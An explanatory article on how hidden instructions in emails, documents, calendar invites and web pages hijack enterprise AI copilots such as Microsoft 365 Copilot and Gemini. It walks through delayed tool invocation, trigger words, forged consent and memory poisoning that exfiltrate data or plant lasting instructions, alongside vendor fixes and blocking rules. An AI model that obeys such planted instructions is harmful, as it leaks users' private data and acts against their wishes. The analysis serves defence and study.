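# Data exfiltration from enterprise AI copilots: delayed tool invocation, embedded widgets and host controls

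## What an enterprise copilot can read and do, and how hidden text takes it over

Data exfiltration from an enterprise AI copilot is the theft of an organisation's information through the AI assistant in its work software. A copilot reads a user's data and acts with the user's permissions. Microsoft 365 Copilot, which works inside Word, Excel, Outlook, Teams and other office programs, is the main example because researchers have repeatedly found ways to get data out of it. They put instructions in an email or document that the assistant would read, and the assistant followed them, so they didn't need a stolen password.

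Researchers reported one such flaw to Microsoft in February 2024 and are still finding others. On 5 December 2026, *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot* (Fadilpašić, 2026) described three more, collectively called ReLeak, all of which Microsoft had already fixed.

### One request from start to finish

In an invented example, Marta buys parts for a bicycle maker. A supplier emails her about a late shipment, and she asks the Copilot pane beside her inbox for a summary and for anything that conflicts with the contract. Outlook is the host application, the program or web page that contains the assistant. The pane is a widget, an AI component that runs inside a host, and much the same pane can run inside Excel Online or SharePoint. Marta's request and everything the assistant does in response make up one turn.

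Microsoft's training material divides what happens next into four steps. First, the host passes the prompt to Copilot. Second, Copilot looks for relevant material (Microsoft calls this grounding) and sends it with the prompt to a large language model. Third, Copilot processes the model's answer, which can involve searching again, checking safety and compliance, and generating commands. Fourth, it returns the reply to the host, which displays it. Software called the orchestrator coordinates these steps and, according to Microsoft's privacy documentation, also logs the interaction for auditors.

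Microsoft's support page lists the sources Copilot can use for grounding: the user's emails, files, chats and meetings, the public web and anything the user attaches. To answer Marta's question, Copilot might fetch the email, the signed contract and a chat in which a colleague mentioned a penalty clause. All of this goes into the context window, together with Marta's question and Microsoft's standing instructions to the model. The model writes its reply from this single body of text.

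A language model only produces text. To do anything else, it makes a tool call, which is a request for the surrounding software to perform an action such as searching mail or writing a memory. The software performs the action and adds the result to the context window, and the model continues from there. One turn can include several such rounds.

Enterprise copilots can now take more actions. In June 2026, RCPmag's *Microsoft Announces General Availability of Copilot Cowork Following Successful Preview* reported the worldwide release of Cowork, an agent for longer tasks. Microsoft's *Application card* for Cowork lists sending emails, posting in Teams, scheduling meetings, managing files and running prompts automatically at set times.

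### Why the model follows the wrong instructions

Suppose the supplier's email has a second paragraph, in white type on a white background. It contains instructions for the assistant to find Marta's correspondence about rival suppliers' prices and put the findings into the web address of a picture in its reply. Marta sees only a note about a late shipment, while the model receives both paragraphs as ordinary text.

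This is indirect prompt injection, in which the assistant reads instructions hidden in content and follows them as if the user had given them. Unlike a direct injection, where the user is the attacker and types the malicious text, an indirect one makes the user the victim, as *The Promptware Kill Chain* (Brodt, Feldman and colleagues, 2026) points out. A single poisoned page or file can reach everyone whose assistant retrieves it. The white type only keeps Marta from noticing the instructions. Microsoft (2025) notes that a plain text file can carry an injection, and so can images, audio and video if the model accepts them.

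Shi, Lin and colleagues (2025), in *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections*, put the situation into a formula:

`y = M(combine(x_user, d_priv, x_adv))`

The software combines the user's request, the private data and the attacker's text into one input for the model. The attack succeeds if the model's output contains a correctly formatted tool call that sends the private data out. The attacker controls only their own text and has to write it without having seen the private data, and often without knowing exactly what the user will ask.

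Nothing in that input firmly marks which part has authority. Older software had a similar problem called SQL injection, in which an attacker types database commands into a web form and the database runs them. Programmers prevent this with parameterised queries, which guarantee that the database treats form entries as data. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, by David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, argues that no such fix is possible inside a language model, because the model does not distinguish instructions from data. It only predicts the next token, a fragment of text, from all the text so far.

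Chat systems tag each stretch of text with a role (system, user, tool output), and some developers train models to rank the system's instructions above the user's and the user's above anything a tool returns. Models follow this ranking unreliably, which makes it a poor basis for security. *Position, Role or Label?* (Laddha, Pradhan and Srivastava, 2026) tested 14 open-weight models on conflicting but harmless instructions, such as how to capitalise field names, and changed only the way each instruction arrived. When two instructions shared a message, the first won in 72% to 95% of the replies that followed either. In one model, Qwen3-14B with its reasoning mode off, the user's instruction beat a contrary one in a tool result just 53% of the time, which is close to chance. By a keyword count, fewer than 3% of the replies mentioned or hedged the conflict, so a user would seldom learn of it.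 These were not attacks, and the largest model had 122 billion parameters, so the results are limited evidence of how often Copilot would give way.

In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) looked for the cause of prompt injection in models' internal activity. They trained classifiers on that activity to detect which role a model assigns to a piece of text, and found that the assignment depends more on how the text sounds than on its role tag. In 1,000 trials where a web page contained a command to upload a secret file, the agent complied 2% of the time when role confusion was lowest and 70% when it was highest.

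The protections vendors add are mostly guardrails, which are filters or trained refusals meant to stop unwanted model behaviour but not guaranteed to do so. Microsoft runs a classifier trained on known injection techniques and marks outside text so the model can recognise it more easily. It calls both defences probabilistic, unlike deterministic ones, which block a given attack every time. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) similarly describes delimiters and role labels as useful engineering but not a hard boundary.

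Guardrails are still worth having. Shi and colleagues found that training Gemini on attacks made it harder to hijack, with no noticeable loss in its other abilities. They also found that models which follow instructions better are sometimes easier to attack, so greater capability will not solve the problem by itself. Attackers can also succeed with a low success rate, because they can send a thousand emails for almost nothing.

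### A deputy with two masters

The white paragraph is dangerous because the assistant has Marta's access, which includes things the paragraph's writer can't reach. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) gave this problem its name and described an example at Tymshare, a company that rented out computer time. Tymshare's compiler had permission to write to its own directory, which held its usage statistics and also the company's billing file. A user who had learned the billing file's name told the compiler to put some debugging output there, and the compiler overwrote the billing data. The user had no permission to write to that file, but the compiler did, and it could not separate the authority it got from the user from the authority it got from the company.

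Hardy's remedy was for each party to give the compiler an unforgeable token that both names a file and grants the right to write to it, so that the compiler never uses one party's rights on another party's file. A copilot is harder to repair because it receives both masters' instructions as text in the same context window. David C therefore calls language models an "inherently confusable deputy" and advises designers to plan for that confusion.

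Microsoft correctly notes in its security documentation that an injection can reach only what the user can open, because Copilot has no access beyond the user's. This limit helps most when the user has narrow access. A finance director or an administrator may be able to open most of what an attacker could want.

According to the same documentation, a person must start or approve actions that could send content out, such as sending an email. Cowork asks for approval in a dialog that previews the message. Users can choose "Don't ask again" for a type of action, which turns off the dialog for that type until the conversation ends. If Marta chooses this for a routine email and Cowork later reads a poisoned message in the same conversation, the hidden instructions could make Cowork send an email without showing her a preview. Microsoft's introduction to Cowork for personal accounts warns that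 Copilot may "be deceived by malicious hidden instructions" and makes users responsible for what Copilot does on their behalf.

### The lethal trifecta

Hijacking an assistant is not enough to steal data. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025), Simon Willison, the software developer who coined the term "prompt injection", lists three capabilities that theft requires. They are access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally in a way that could carry data out. This theft would fail if any one were missing, but Marta's copilot has all three. It can read her price correspondence, it has read the supplier's email, and a picture in its reply can make her computer contact a server the attacker chose.

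The security researcher Johann Rehberger would take away the outgoing channel, which he calls the only part that is "realistically enforceable" in Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON*, the write-up of a 2026 conference talk on attacks against Microsoft's copilots. Microsoft 365 Copilot has the other two by default, because its job is to read mail, chats and shared documents, and much of that material comes from other people.

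The reason is that whether the model follows the white paragraph is a matter of probability, while ordinary software controls whether Marta's browser contacts an unknown server, and that software can check the address and block the request. One such check is a Content Security Policy (CSP), a web page's rules for which addresses the browser may load resources from. If the policy of the page around Marta's chat pane doesn't allow the attacker's server, the browser does not fetch the picture, whatever the model wrote.

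An organisation could instead keep private data from Copilot by turning off a Microsoft setting called Work IQ. Copilot then answers without the user's mail, files, chats and meetings, and draws on the web, the user's profile and whatever the user attaches. Marta could still attach the supplier's email and get a summary, but to ask whether it conflicts with the contract, she would have to find the contract herself. Finding information is a large part of what her employer pays Copilot to do.

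An administrator can instead remove untrusted content by setting a data-loss-prevention rule that keeps Copilot from using external email. Microsoft 365 for IT Pros' *Microsoft Defender for Office 365 Blocks Prompt Injections* (2026) recommends this option alongside filtering at the mailbox. The rule also covers messages that have already arrived. But the supplier is external, so Marta loses her summary altogether. Attackers can also plant text in shared documents and web pages, which the rule doesn't cover.

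David C passes on a subtler idea, from an exchange between Willison and Baibhav Bista, that when a model processes information from some party, its privileges should drop to that party's level. The assistant could then summarise the supplier's email but could not open anything the supplier isn't allowed to see. That would have stopped the theft, but it would also have ruled out Marta's question, which needs both the email and the contract. Much of the value of an enterprise copilot comes from combining inside and outside material, so Rehberger's answer seems right for a general office assistant, though not necessarily for every narrower tool.

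Restrictions on exfiltration can be enforced, but not easily. An exfiltration channel is any route by which data can reach an outsider, and Willison considers the possible routes almost limitless. Microsoft's list includes images, links, tools that write to public places, and even tool calls that leak one bit at a time because an outsider can observe whether they happen. Some channels can't be removed, because an agent built to send email must be able to send it. Vendors have mostly closed channels in response to reported attacks. Willison counted more than a dozen affected products between April 2023 and mid-2025, and in almost all of them the vendor promptly fixed the flaw, usually by closing the route out. Microsoft's guidance tells developers to assume that indirect prompt injection is inevitable and to design systems that contain it.

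### One click or none

If the hidden paragraph had produced a link instead of a picture, no data would have left the company until Marta clicked it, making this a one-click attack. *Trust No AI* (2024) describes how the flaw from February 2024 worked this way. A phishing email made Copilot search the victim's inbox and put what it found, in invisible characters, into a link in its reply. Microsoft fixed the flaw in July 2024.

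A zero-click attack needs no action from the victim beyond ordinary use of the assistant. The picture in Marta's reply is an example, because her browser would load it automatically. *EchoLeak* (2025) documents an early real case in Copilot. Microsoft patched the flaw before the details became public. In one of Rehberger's demonstrations, the victim opened a shared Word document and typed only a greeting to Copilot, which then found an email and leaked its contents. Microsoft fixed that flaw on 5 March 2026.

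The ReLeak attacks are called "zero-click", but they still depend on the user asking Copilot for something. AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026) describes how the malicious email sits unopened in the inbox until Copilot retrieves it to answer a legitimate request. Advice to staff about suspicious links would not have helped, since the user did not have to click a link or open the email. A scheduled prompt, such as an inbox summary that runs every morning, could retrieve the email without a new request from the user. Microsoft closed the three routes on 17 September, 11 November and 15 November 2026, and the researchers at Cato AI Labs know of no real attacks that used them.

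## Delayed tool invocation: instructions that wait for a later turn

In November 2023, Johann Rehberger was testing Bard, the Google assistant now called Gemini. Bard could look up flights, hotels and YouTube videos through add-ons that Google called extensions. The Workspace extension gave it access to the user's own email and documents. When Rehberger fed Bard hidden instructions to use its extensions, it called four of them in one go but never called Workspace.

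In Embrace The Red's *Google Gemini* (2024), Rehberger concludes that Google had designed Gemini not to open the user's private data during a turn in which untrusted text entered the conversation. He considered this an interesting defence that other vendors had not yet adopted. But the untrusted text stayed in the conversation after that turn, when the protection no longer applied.

First, the attacker sends the victim an email containing an instruction for Gemini to carry out the next time the victim asks for something. Second, the victim asks Gemini to summarise the email. Third, the instruction becomes part of the conversation, where the victim may not notice it, but Gemini does not call Workspace yet because the protection applies. Fourth, the victim asks another question, and Gemini calls Workspace. In the demonstration, Gemini found a document about cats in Rehberger's files and printed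 the text in the chat.

This is delayed tool invocation, in which an attacker plants an instruction in one turn that triggers a tool call in a later one. The cat document appeared only on the victim's screen, because Google had already closed the image route that could have exfiltrated it. Rehberger warned that the technique would do much more harm if a new exfiltration route appeared, or if Google added extensions that could write data as well as read it. Google confirmed that it was tracking the problem, but the technique still worked more than a year later.

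### How long should a block last?

A small model shows what went wrong. Number the turns of a conversation 1, 2, 3 and so on, and let U(t) be true if untrusted text enters at turn t. Call a tool sensitive if it can read private data or change something. Now compare two rules:

- Rule 1: at turn t, block sensitive tools if U(t) is true.
- Rule 2: at turn t, block sensitive tools if U(s) is true for any s ≤ t.

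Gemini appeared to follow Rule 1 in 2023. Suppose Marta, the buyer at the bicycle maker, asks for a summary of her supplier's email. The email contains a hidden instruction to search her mail for rival suppliers' prices the next time she writes anything. She reads the summary and types a thank-you.

| Turn | What happens | U(t) | Rule 1 | Rule 2 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Copilot reads the email and summarises it | True | Blocks the search | Blocks the search |
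| 2 | Marta says thanks, and the model requests the search | False | Allows the search | Blocks the search |

Rule 1 depends only on what arrived in the current turn, but the model's input at turn 2 still includes everything from turn 1. Rule 2 blocks the search from turn 2 onward, whether or not the model follows the instruction.

Suppose the supplier is honest. Marta gets her summary at turn 1, and at turn 2 she asks Copilot to find the contract so that she can check the penalty clause. Rule 1 allows this. Rule 2 blocks it for as long as the email is in the conversation. If she starts a new conversation, Copilot can find the contract, but the email is no longer there, and adding it brings the block back. Her original request, for a summary and any conflicts with the contract in a single turn, would fail under both rules.

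Rule 2 is more likely to block sensitive tools as a conversation gets longer. If each turn independently has a 30% chance of bringing in outside text, Rule 1 blocks these tools in 30% of turns. Under Rule 2, they still work at turn t only if none of the first t turns brought in outside text. The probability of that is 0.7^t, which is 49% at the second turn and 17% at the fifth. An assistant that spends much of its time reading mail probably brings in outside text in more than 30% of turns.

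A softer version of Rule 2 requires the user's confirmation instead of blocking the tool call. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Gemini's Memory with Prompt Injection and Delayed Tool Invocation* recommends this for every sensitive tool call once untrusted data has entered the chat. Marta would then get her contract after clicking to confirm.

*ATLAS* (2020), a regularly updated catalogue of attacks on AI systems from the American research organisation MITRE, has contained similar advice since October 2025. It suggests blocking automatic tool calls, or requiring confirmation, once untrusted data enters the model's context. For actions with serious consequences, it suggests considering confirmation every time.

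In November 2025 MITRE also gave delayed invocation its own entry, AML.T0094, "Delay Execution of LLM Instructions". According to the entry, the technique can defeat controls that withhold tools during a turn "that has untrusted data in context". Read literally, this wording describes Rule 2, since the supplier's email is still in context when Marta says thanks. The attack succeeds when the software checks only for untrusted data that arrived in the current turn. MITRE grades the technique "Demonstrated", a step below "Realized", which is for techniques attackers have used in real incidents.

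Even a strict Rule 2 has gaps. The software may fail to recognise untrusted text, such as paragraphs from a supplier that a colleague pasted into their own document. The rule also doesn't protect private data that is already in the conversation. If Marta opens the contract at turn 1 and the poisoned email at turn 2, the attacker only needs a way to send the contract out and doesn't need another search to find it.

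The count also restarts with each new conversation, so an instruction stored in long-term memory escapes the rule. This was possible in Microsoft 365 Copilot until Microsoft fixed the flaw in December 2025. Information-flow systems, which track where each piece of data came from, are designed to give comparable protection while blocking less.

### What sets the instruction off

Rehberger's first version ran on the user's next request, whatever it was. This trigger rarely fails, since people who ask an assistant one question often ask another. But if the next request brings in new outside text, such as a second email, Rule 1 blocks the tools again. The user is also waiting for an answer and will probably notice if an unrelated document appears instead.

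A keyword can avoid both problems. Nassi, Cohen and Yair (2025), in *Invitation Is All You Need!*, attacked Gemini with instructions that waited for polite words such as "thanks" or "great". A thank-you gives the assistant no reason to fetch anything, so U(t) stays false. It also tends to come when users have what they wanted and have stopped reading closely. Because some users never thank an assistant, two of the planted instructions were triggered by any English word of more than two letters, which almost every reply contains.

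The attacker can also make the assistant ask a question and wait for the answer. Rehberger did this in the 2025 demonstration against Gemini's long-term memory, which stores facts about the user for later conversations. Gemini did not normally call its memory tool while processing untrusted data, so Rehberger delayed the call until the user answered.

The victim uploaded a document about Albert Einstein and asked for a summary. Hidden text in the document made Gemini end the summary with an instruction to save certain facts if the user gave one of several short answers, and an offer to tell the user more about Einstein. "Yes", "sure" and "no" all triggered the save. Gemini then recorded that the user was 102 years old and thought the earth was flat. When Rehberger later asked for the user's age, Gemini answered 102.

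Declining the offer did not protect the victim, since "no" worked as well as "yes". The victim could still have noticed the instruction, which was visible in the summary, or the notice that Gemini displays when it saves a memory. Rehberger reported the flaw in December 2024. Google rated its likelihood and impact as low, and left open whether it would fix the flaw. Rehberger agreed that the attack relied on tricking the user into continuing the conversation, but thought this would not be difficult, and pointed out that false memories could seriously affect the user.

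### Why a reply looks like consent

In the Einstein demonstration, the user agrees to hear more about Einstein, and Gemini treats the answer as permission to save a memory. The word "yes" could mean either. The attacker exploits the model's ability to connect a short reply with something earlier in the conversation. Models need this ability because people often give assistants conditional orders, such as to send a draft once they approve it.

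Software that applies Rule 1 can't tell the difference any better, because the current turn contains a real message from the user and no new outside text. A tool call in that turn therefore looks like the user's decision, even though the attacker wrote the condition that triggered it.

According to Rehberger's Embrace The Red, attackers often have the model repeat the planted instruction in its reply, which makes the attack more likely to work. Rehberger gives no figures, but the effect is plausible for two reasons. Repetition moves the instruction from an outsider's document into the assistant's own reply, and experiments by Ye and colleagues suggest that a model identifies the speaker more by the style of the text than by its label. Repetition also puts the instruction closer to the user's next message.

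In some assistants the attack works only if the output repeats the email's instruction, because the component that reads the email passes only its output to the component that calls the other tools. The user may therefore see the instruction. Rehberger expects this to become less of a problem for attackers as models handle longer contexts, since an instruction is harder to spot in a long reply.

### Getting past a control or a guardrail

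A delay can defeat an enforced control or a guardrail, and the fix depends on which one failed. In 2023, Gemini appears to have had an enforced control whose scope was too narrow. The attack avoided it by delaying the tool call until a turn that the control did not cover. Google could fix this by extending the control to later turns, which would work however the attacker phrased the instruction.

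Rehberger says that delayed invocation gets past guardrails more often, and that it did so with Copilot. A model may refuse a suspicious action when the instruction comes directly from a document, yet perform the same action when it seems to follow from the user's reply. More training or filtering can reduce the advantage that the delay gives an attacker.

In one of Rehberger's examples, the victim uploaded a file to the consumer version of Copilot in Microsoft's Edge browser and asked for a summary. A planted instruction took effect only when the victim replied "yes". Copilot then sent the facts it had stored about the victim to Rehberger's server by opening a web address that contained them.

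When Rehberger tried again a few weeks before presenting the attack in 2026, Copilot consistently blocked the file, and Microsoft could no longer reproduce the attack either. Rehberger thinks Microsoft most likely added guardrails and input filtering. If so, the change stops that file and probably others like it, but a differently worded file might still get through.

Outside observers often find it hard to tell which protection an attack has passed, because both can produce the same refusal. The evidence for an enforced rule in Gemini is better than usual because the hidden instructions reached four other extensions and failed to reach only the one with private data.

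Google makes a similar distinction. Gavish (2026), in *Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections*, classes user confirmation and policies on tool chaining as deterministic defences. Engineers can change these quickly through the settings of a central policy engine, whereas machine-learning defences take longer to update because Google has to retrain them on new examples.

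### Fourteen scenarios from a calendar invitation

Nassi and colleagues had to get past a stronger design than the one Rehberger faced in 2023. In Gemini, a central model called the orchestrator plans the work and calls specialised agents for services such as mail, the calendar and smart-home devices. Only the orchestrator can start an agent, and each agent returns only its output, without sharing its working context.

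A poisoned calendar entry can make the calendar agent output an instruction to open the user's windows when the user says thanks. The calendar agent can't open them itself, but the orchestrator receives that output and can call the smart-home agent. In the demonstration, the user asked about upcoming events and thanked Gemini for the answer, and Gemini opened the windows.

Brodt and colleagues describe delayed invocation as a way around plan-then-execute designs, which stop an agent from changing its plan after it has read untrusted data. The first turn's plan doesn't change, but the orchestrator makes a new plan for the second turn with the planted instruction already in its context.

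The attack that stole calendar data used two invitations. The first made Gemini put the titles of the user's meetings into a web address whenever it listed the calendar. The second made Gemini open that address in the phone's browser when the user said "thanks", which sent the titles of six meetings to the receiving server. A similar attack needed only one email and leaked the subject line of another message.

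The paper rates the risk of 14 scenarios. Four are critical (stealing emails, streaming video of the user, opening the windows, and a worm that spreads by email), two are very high, four high, three medium and one low. The paper says 73% are rated high or above, but ten out of fourteen is 71%. The researchers did not carry out every scenario. They took the false-memory scenario from Rehberger's work, and they inferred that the worm was possible because they had succeeded in stealing email data.

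Each rating combines an impact score with a likelihood score, which averages six factors: equipment, expertise, opportunity, knowledge of the target, preparation time and how much the user has to do. Almost every scenario is rated "very likely", because the attacker needs only a laptop, a computer-science graduate's skills, the victim's email address and less than a day. The ratings are good evidence that the attacks were easy to attempt, but none of the six factors measures how often Gemini obeyed the planted text. The study considered private users of Gemini, so it doesn't estimate the risk to a company.

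The researchers reported their findings to Google on 22 February 2025. In its response, which the paper prints in full, Google called the scenarios "theoretical", though the researchers had sent videos of attacks working on their own accounts. Google said it had required confirmation for more operations involving private data, other applications and devices, improved its detection of suspicious links, and added a classifier to filter out malicious instructions. It said all users had these protections before the paper came out in August 2025, and that it had also rerun the original attacks with many variations.

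Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (June 2025) gives deleting a calendar event as an example of an action that may require confirmation.

Nassi and colleagues also estimated the risk that would remain if a vendor adopted five protections together, including a policy, close to Rule 2, against launching agents after a tool has brought in external data. They concluded that every type of attack would become "unlikely" and that no scenario would rate above medium risk. They reasoned that an attacker would then need advanced AI expertise, a cluster of graphics processors, detailed knowledge of the guardrails and perhaps months of preparation.

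### When the user agrees to something else

Google's actual defences were easier to beat than that. *Gemini's Secret Affair*, published on 3 June 2026 by SafeBreach, the security company where Yair works, describes a second round of attacks, which SafeBreach had reported to Google on 17 August 2025. The result doesn't refute the estimate, because Google had not adopted exactly the five protections it covered. But SafeBreach developed the new attack by trial and error against the live product, and there is no sign that it needed a cluster of processors or inside knowledge.

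The instructions now arrived in phone notifications. Anyone who could send the victim a text, WhatsApp or Slack message could include instructions in it, and they entered the conversation when the victim asked Gemini to read out notifications. The work focused on Gemini's voice assistant, which opens the microphone after asking a question, encouraging the user to reply.

Ordinary delayed invocation no longer worked. Gemini refused every time the planted text told it to open a window after the user said "yes" or "thanks". It did open the window if the user asked directly, or said yes after Gemini asked whether to open it. SafeBreach inferred that a security check was probably comparing the user's last message with Gemini's last output to see whether a bare "yes" made sense as permission.

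This improved on Rule 1 because the user's reply now had to match a question about the action, but the attacker could influence that question. SafeBreach made Gemini produce a permission request that the user would not notice or understand, together with an ordinary question. When the user said yes to the ordinary question, the check apparently matched that answer to the permission request.

With this method, SafeBreach opened windows, started a Zoom video stream, saved a false name to Gemini's long-term memory and scheduled a daily task to read the user's recent messages. Ordinary delayed invocation had not achieved either of the last two in the earlier research. SafeBreach therefore suspected that Gemini applied a stricter check to lasting changes, though the forged consent passed that check too. Google may have tightened the memory tool after Rehberger's report, but SafeBreach could only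 guess at this from Gemini's behaviour.

On 14 November 2025 Google confirmed that improvements to its content classifier had mitigated these attacks. The classifier is meant to detect planted text in incoming content. If it misses a new version, the user's protection again depends on how Gemini establishes consent, and Google did not mention any change to that in its confirmation.

A confirmation would be more dependable if ordinary software showed it in a dialog outside the model's reply and named the exact action. The attacker could still propose an action but could not disguise what the user was approving. Cowork's approval dialog for outgoing email works this way.

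Delayed invocation has also remained useful against other products. [un]prompted's *Your Agent Works for Me Now* (2026), the abstract of a conference talk, lists it as one of several techniques that bypass existing mitigations, with Gemini and Copilot among the targets. It adds that new AI systems keep reintroducing known types of flaw even where simple fixes exist.

### Reprompt: a check on the first request only

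*Reprompt* (2026), published in January by the data-security company Varonis, describes an attack on Microsoft's consumer assistant, Copilot Personal, that exploited a similar mistake without waiting for the user to write again. The attack began when the user clicked once on a genuine Microsoft link. The link contained a prompt, which Copilot ran as though the user had typed it.

The prompt told Copilot to fetch a web address containing information about the user. In a test, Copilot's safeguard removed a secret phrase from the address before the request was made, but the safeguard checked only the first request. When Copilot repeated the request, it sent the phrase unaltered. Varonis suspects that Microsoft limited the check to save time.

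Once Copilot had contacted the attacker's server, the server could reply with another instruction. It sent a new one after each answer from Copilot and could base it on the information already received. In the demonstration, it requested in stages the time, the user's location, any other information Copilot had about the user, and a summary of the user's last conversation. The exchange continued even if the user closed the chat.

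Reprompt could happen entirely after a single prompt, so it is not delayed tool invocation in the strict sense. But in both attacks, a safeguard applied at one moment and the attacker acted later. Rule 2 would have helped only from the second stage on, if it had counted web requests as sensitive and the server's replies as untrusted text. The rule would have allowed the first request because the opening prompt looked like the user's own. Varonis recommends that vendors treat prompts from links as untrusted too, and keep safeguards active through repeated and follow-up requests.

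The later instructions also made the theft harder to investigate because they came from the server, so someone who inspected the original link would have found only the first request. Varonis reported in January 2026 that Microsoft had patched the flaw and that it had not affected enterprise customers using Microsoft 365 Copilot.

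## Stored memories that carry an instruction into later conversations

In delayed tool invocation, the planted text normally has to take effect before the user leaves the conversation, because the next one starts with an empty history. An instruction saved to long-term memory can take effect later, because the assistant loads stored memories into every new conversation.

Microsoft announced memory for Microsoft 365 Copilot on 14 July 2025 and turned it on by default, according to Office 365 for IT Pros' *Microsoft Introduces Copilot Memory* (2025). The model saves a memory by calling a tool named `record_memory`. Suppose Marta, the buyer at the bicycle maker, tells Copilot to remember that she wants prices in euros. The model passes one line of text to the tool, and the software stores it in a hidden folder in her mailbox. When she starts another chat, the software adds the line to the context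 window, so she gets prices in euros without asking again.

According to Microsoft's documentation, a memory saved by Copilot stays until the user deletes it in the settings. Deleting the chat it came from does not remove it, and switching the memory feature off stops Copilot from using it but does not delete it. An employer's rule for deleting old chats does not apply to memories either. Administrators can turn memory off for everyone, or find and delete a user's memories with Microsoft's search tools, but they cannot restrict what kinds of information Copilot saves.

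### How a delay of one turn becomes indefinite

Slightly simplified, the model's input at turn t of conversation k is:

`input(k, t) = standing instructions + saved memories + turns 1 to t of conversation k`

An attacker who plants an instruction in a conversation can use it only until that conversation ends. If the attacker gets the instruction into the saved memories, the model receives it at every turn of every later conversation until someone deletes the memory.

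Rule 2 resets its count of outside text at the start of each conversation, so it allows every tool in conversation 6. The software could label each memory saved while outside text was present and treat any conversation that loads a labeled memory as exposed. But then one harmless memory, saved while a supplier's email was open, would block Marta's tools in every chat she started afterward.

It is much easier to stop the memory from being saved in the first place. If Rule 2 treats `record_memory` as a sensitive tool, Copilot cannot save anything after reading the supplier's email. Marta can open a new chat and tell Copilot what to remember, which takes a few seconds.

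### The biography and the password

Johann Rehberger sent Microsoft a full demonstration of a persistent attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot on 19 November 2025. He calls this kind of attack SpAIware, a name he had used in September 2024 for an attack on the memory of OpenAI's ChatGPT app for Macs. That same month, OpenAI closed the route the attack used to send data out of the app.

Embrace The Red documents the Copilot version, in which a user uploads a harmless-looking biography of Albert Einstein with an instruction buried in the middle and asks for a summary. Copilot writes an ordinary summary and ends by asking whether the information was helpful. A reply of either "yes" or "no" makes Copilot save a memory.

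So far this resembles Rehberger's earlier Gemini demonstration, except that the memories planted there were false facts about the user. Here the memory was a standing instruction, worded as the user's preference, to display passwords and codes immediately in a preview panel and to load the panel's font from Rehberger's server.

When the user pastes a secret into a later conversation, Copilot follows the instruction in the memory and opens the panel. The request for the font then carries the secret to the server.

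The password could have been created after the user read the biography. This attack keeps collecting whatever the user types in later, unlike an attack confined to one conversation, which takes what the assistant can reach at that moment. The user supplies the secret, so the attack doesn't have to search for it. Copilot could open the preview without a tool call, so neither Rule 1 nor Rule 2 would have stopped the theft at that stage.

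Rehberger describes the memory write as silent, meaning that Copilot did not ask first. However, "Memory updated" appeared in small type below the user's message, and the entry was listed with the other saved memories in the settings. The preview panel also appeared on screen during the theft. A watchful user might have noticed any of these, but Copilot shows the same "Memory updated" notice after saving a real preference.

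Other demonstrations were easier to notice. In one, a planted memory that the user preferred Mandarin Chinese made Copilot answer English questions in Mandarin. Rehberger could also make Copilot delete memories. An attacker could use this to remove the user's real preferences, or to hide how a theft happened by deleting the planted memory afterward.

Microsoft told Rehberger in December 2025 that it had fixed both the adding and the deleting of memories, and it reported the persistent attack fixed on 6 December. He thinks the fix probably consists of more training and more blocking of incoming content, which would make it a guardrail. The preview route stayed open until 5 March 2026, so a memory planted before the December fix could have kept leaking secrets for three more months, unless Microsoft also screened or removed memories already stored. Rehberger reports no real victims.

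In June, Microsoft (2026) described its current protections for memory in Microsoft 365. Classifiers look for injected instructions and remove them before anything is saved. Another check, Task Adherence, compares each explicit memory write with what the user was trying to do. This addresses the right weakness, because a user who answers a question about Einstein is not trying to change how Copilot handles passwords. Microsoft gives no figures for how often this check works. Its description of Task Adherence covers only explicit writes, but Copilot also infers details about users from their past chats.

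The June account credits two researchers besides Rehberger. One of them, the Norwegian data scientist Håkon Måløy, had found a different method of attack. When a user asked Copilot to summarise a malicious web page, the page could make Copilot save a memory that persisted across the user's web and work sessions. iTnews' *Microsoft can't kill dogged researcher's Copilot for Word worm* reported that Microsoft had fixed this for every organisation, with no action needed from customers. Måløy's blog post, En Klype Salt's *Context Collapse, Part 3* (2026), indicates that the flaw was no longer exploitable by 28 July 2026.

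### The consumer product and CoSnitch

Microsoft's Copilot for personal accounts has its own memory tools for saving, searching and deleting "durable facts". Rehberger showed that an uploaded file could make it save false ones. Microsoft reported this flaw fixed on 6 December 2025, the same day as the one behind the persistent attack on the enterprise product.

Late in 2025 Microsoft also gave the Copilot in its Edge browser a tool for opening web addresses. Rehberger used it in the attack where a "yes" from the user sent their stored facts to his server, though the instruction came from the uploaded file rather than from memory. Embrace The Red leaves open whether anyone could have combined the two flaws into a lasting theft like the one in the enterprise product, because Microsoft may have fixed the memory flaw before it introduced the navigation tool. The Edge attack no longer works, but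 it has no published fix date.

A more serious consumer case followed in August. Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) describes three flaws in Copilot Personal, which Microsoft tracks together as CVE-2026-24301:

- A link could open Copilot and run the attacker's prompt immediately, without the user pressing Enter.
- That prompt could search services the user had connected, such as Gmail and Google Drive, and send out the results in a web address that Copilot fetched.
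- Hidden text in a web page could write to the user's memory when the user asked Copilot to summarise the page.

Copilot saved the attacker's text to memory in the same turn in which it read the page, then returned a normal summary, so exploiting the memory flaw required no delay. Even Rule 1, which considers only what arrived in the current turn, would have prevented the save if it had covered the memory tool.

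Varonis showed that a planted memory could make Copilot tell the user that a known security flaw posed no risk. Varonis also lists forwarding Copilot's later output to the attacker as a possibility, but its memory demonstrations covered only what Copilot told the user.

The planted memory survived password changes, the ending of all login sessions and the re-enrolment of the user's device. Security teams take these steps after a break-in to lock out someone using a stolen password or session, but this attacker had never logged in. The instruction was part of the user's own data, and Copilot loaded it whenever the user came back. Varonis calls such a memory permanent, although the user can delete it by hand in the settings. Few people are likely to think of that while changing passwords.

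Varonis reported CoSnitch in December 2025, and Microsoft shipped the patches on 18 August 2026. Fame Systems, a German site, mentions a quiet partial fix in February, which Varonis's account leaves out. Microsoft made the change on its own servers, according to TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions*, so users had nothing to install. Varonis has seen no sign of real attacks. A patch that blocks new entries does not necessarily remove old ones, so anyone worried about a page they summarised before the fix may still want to check their saved memories.

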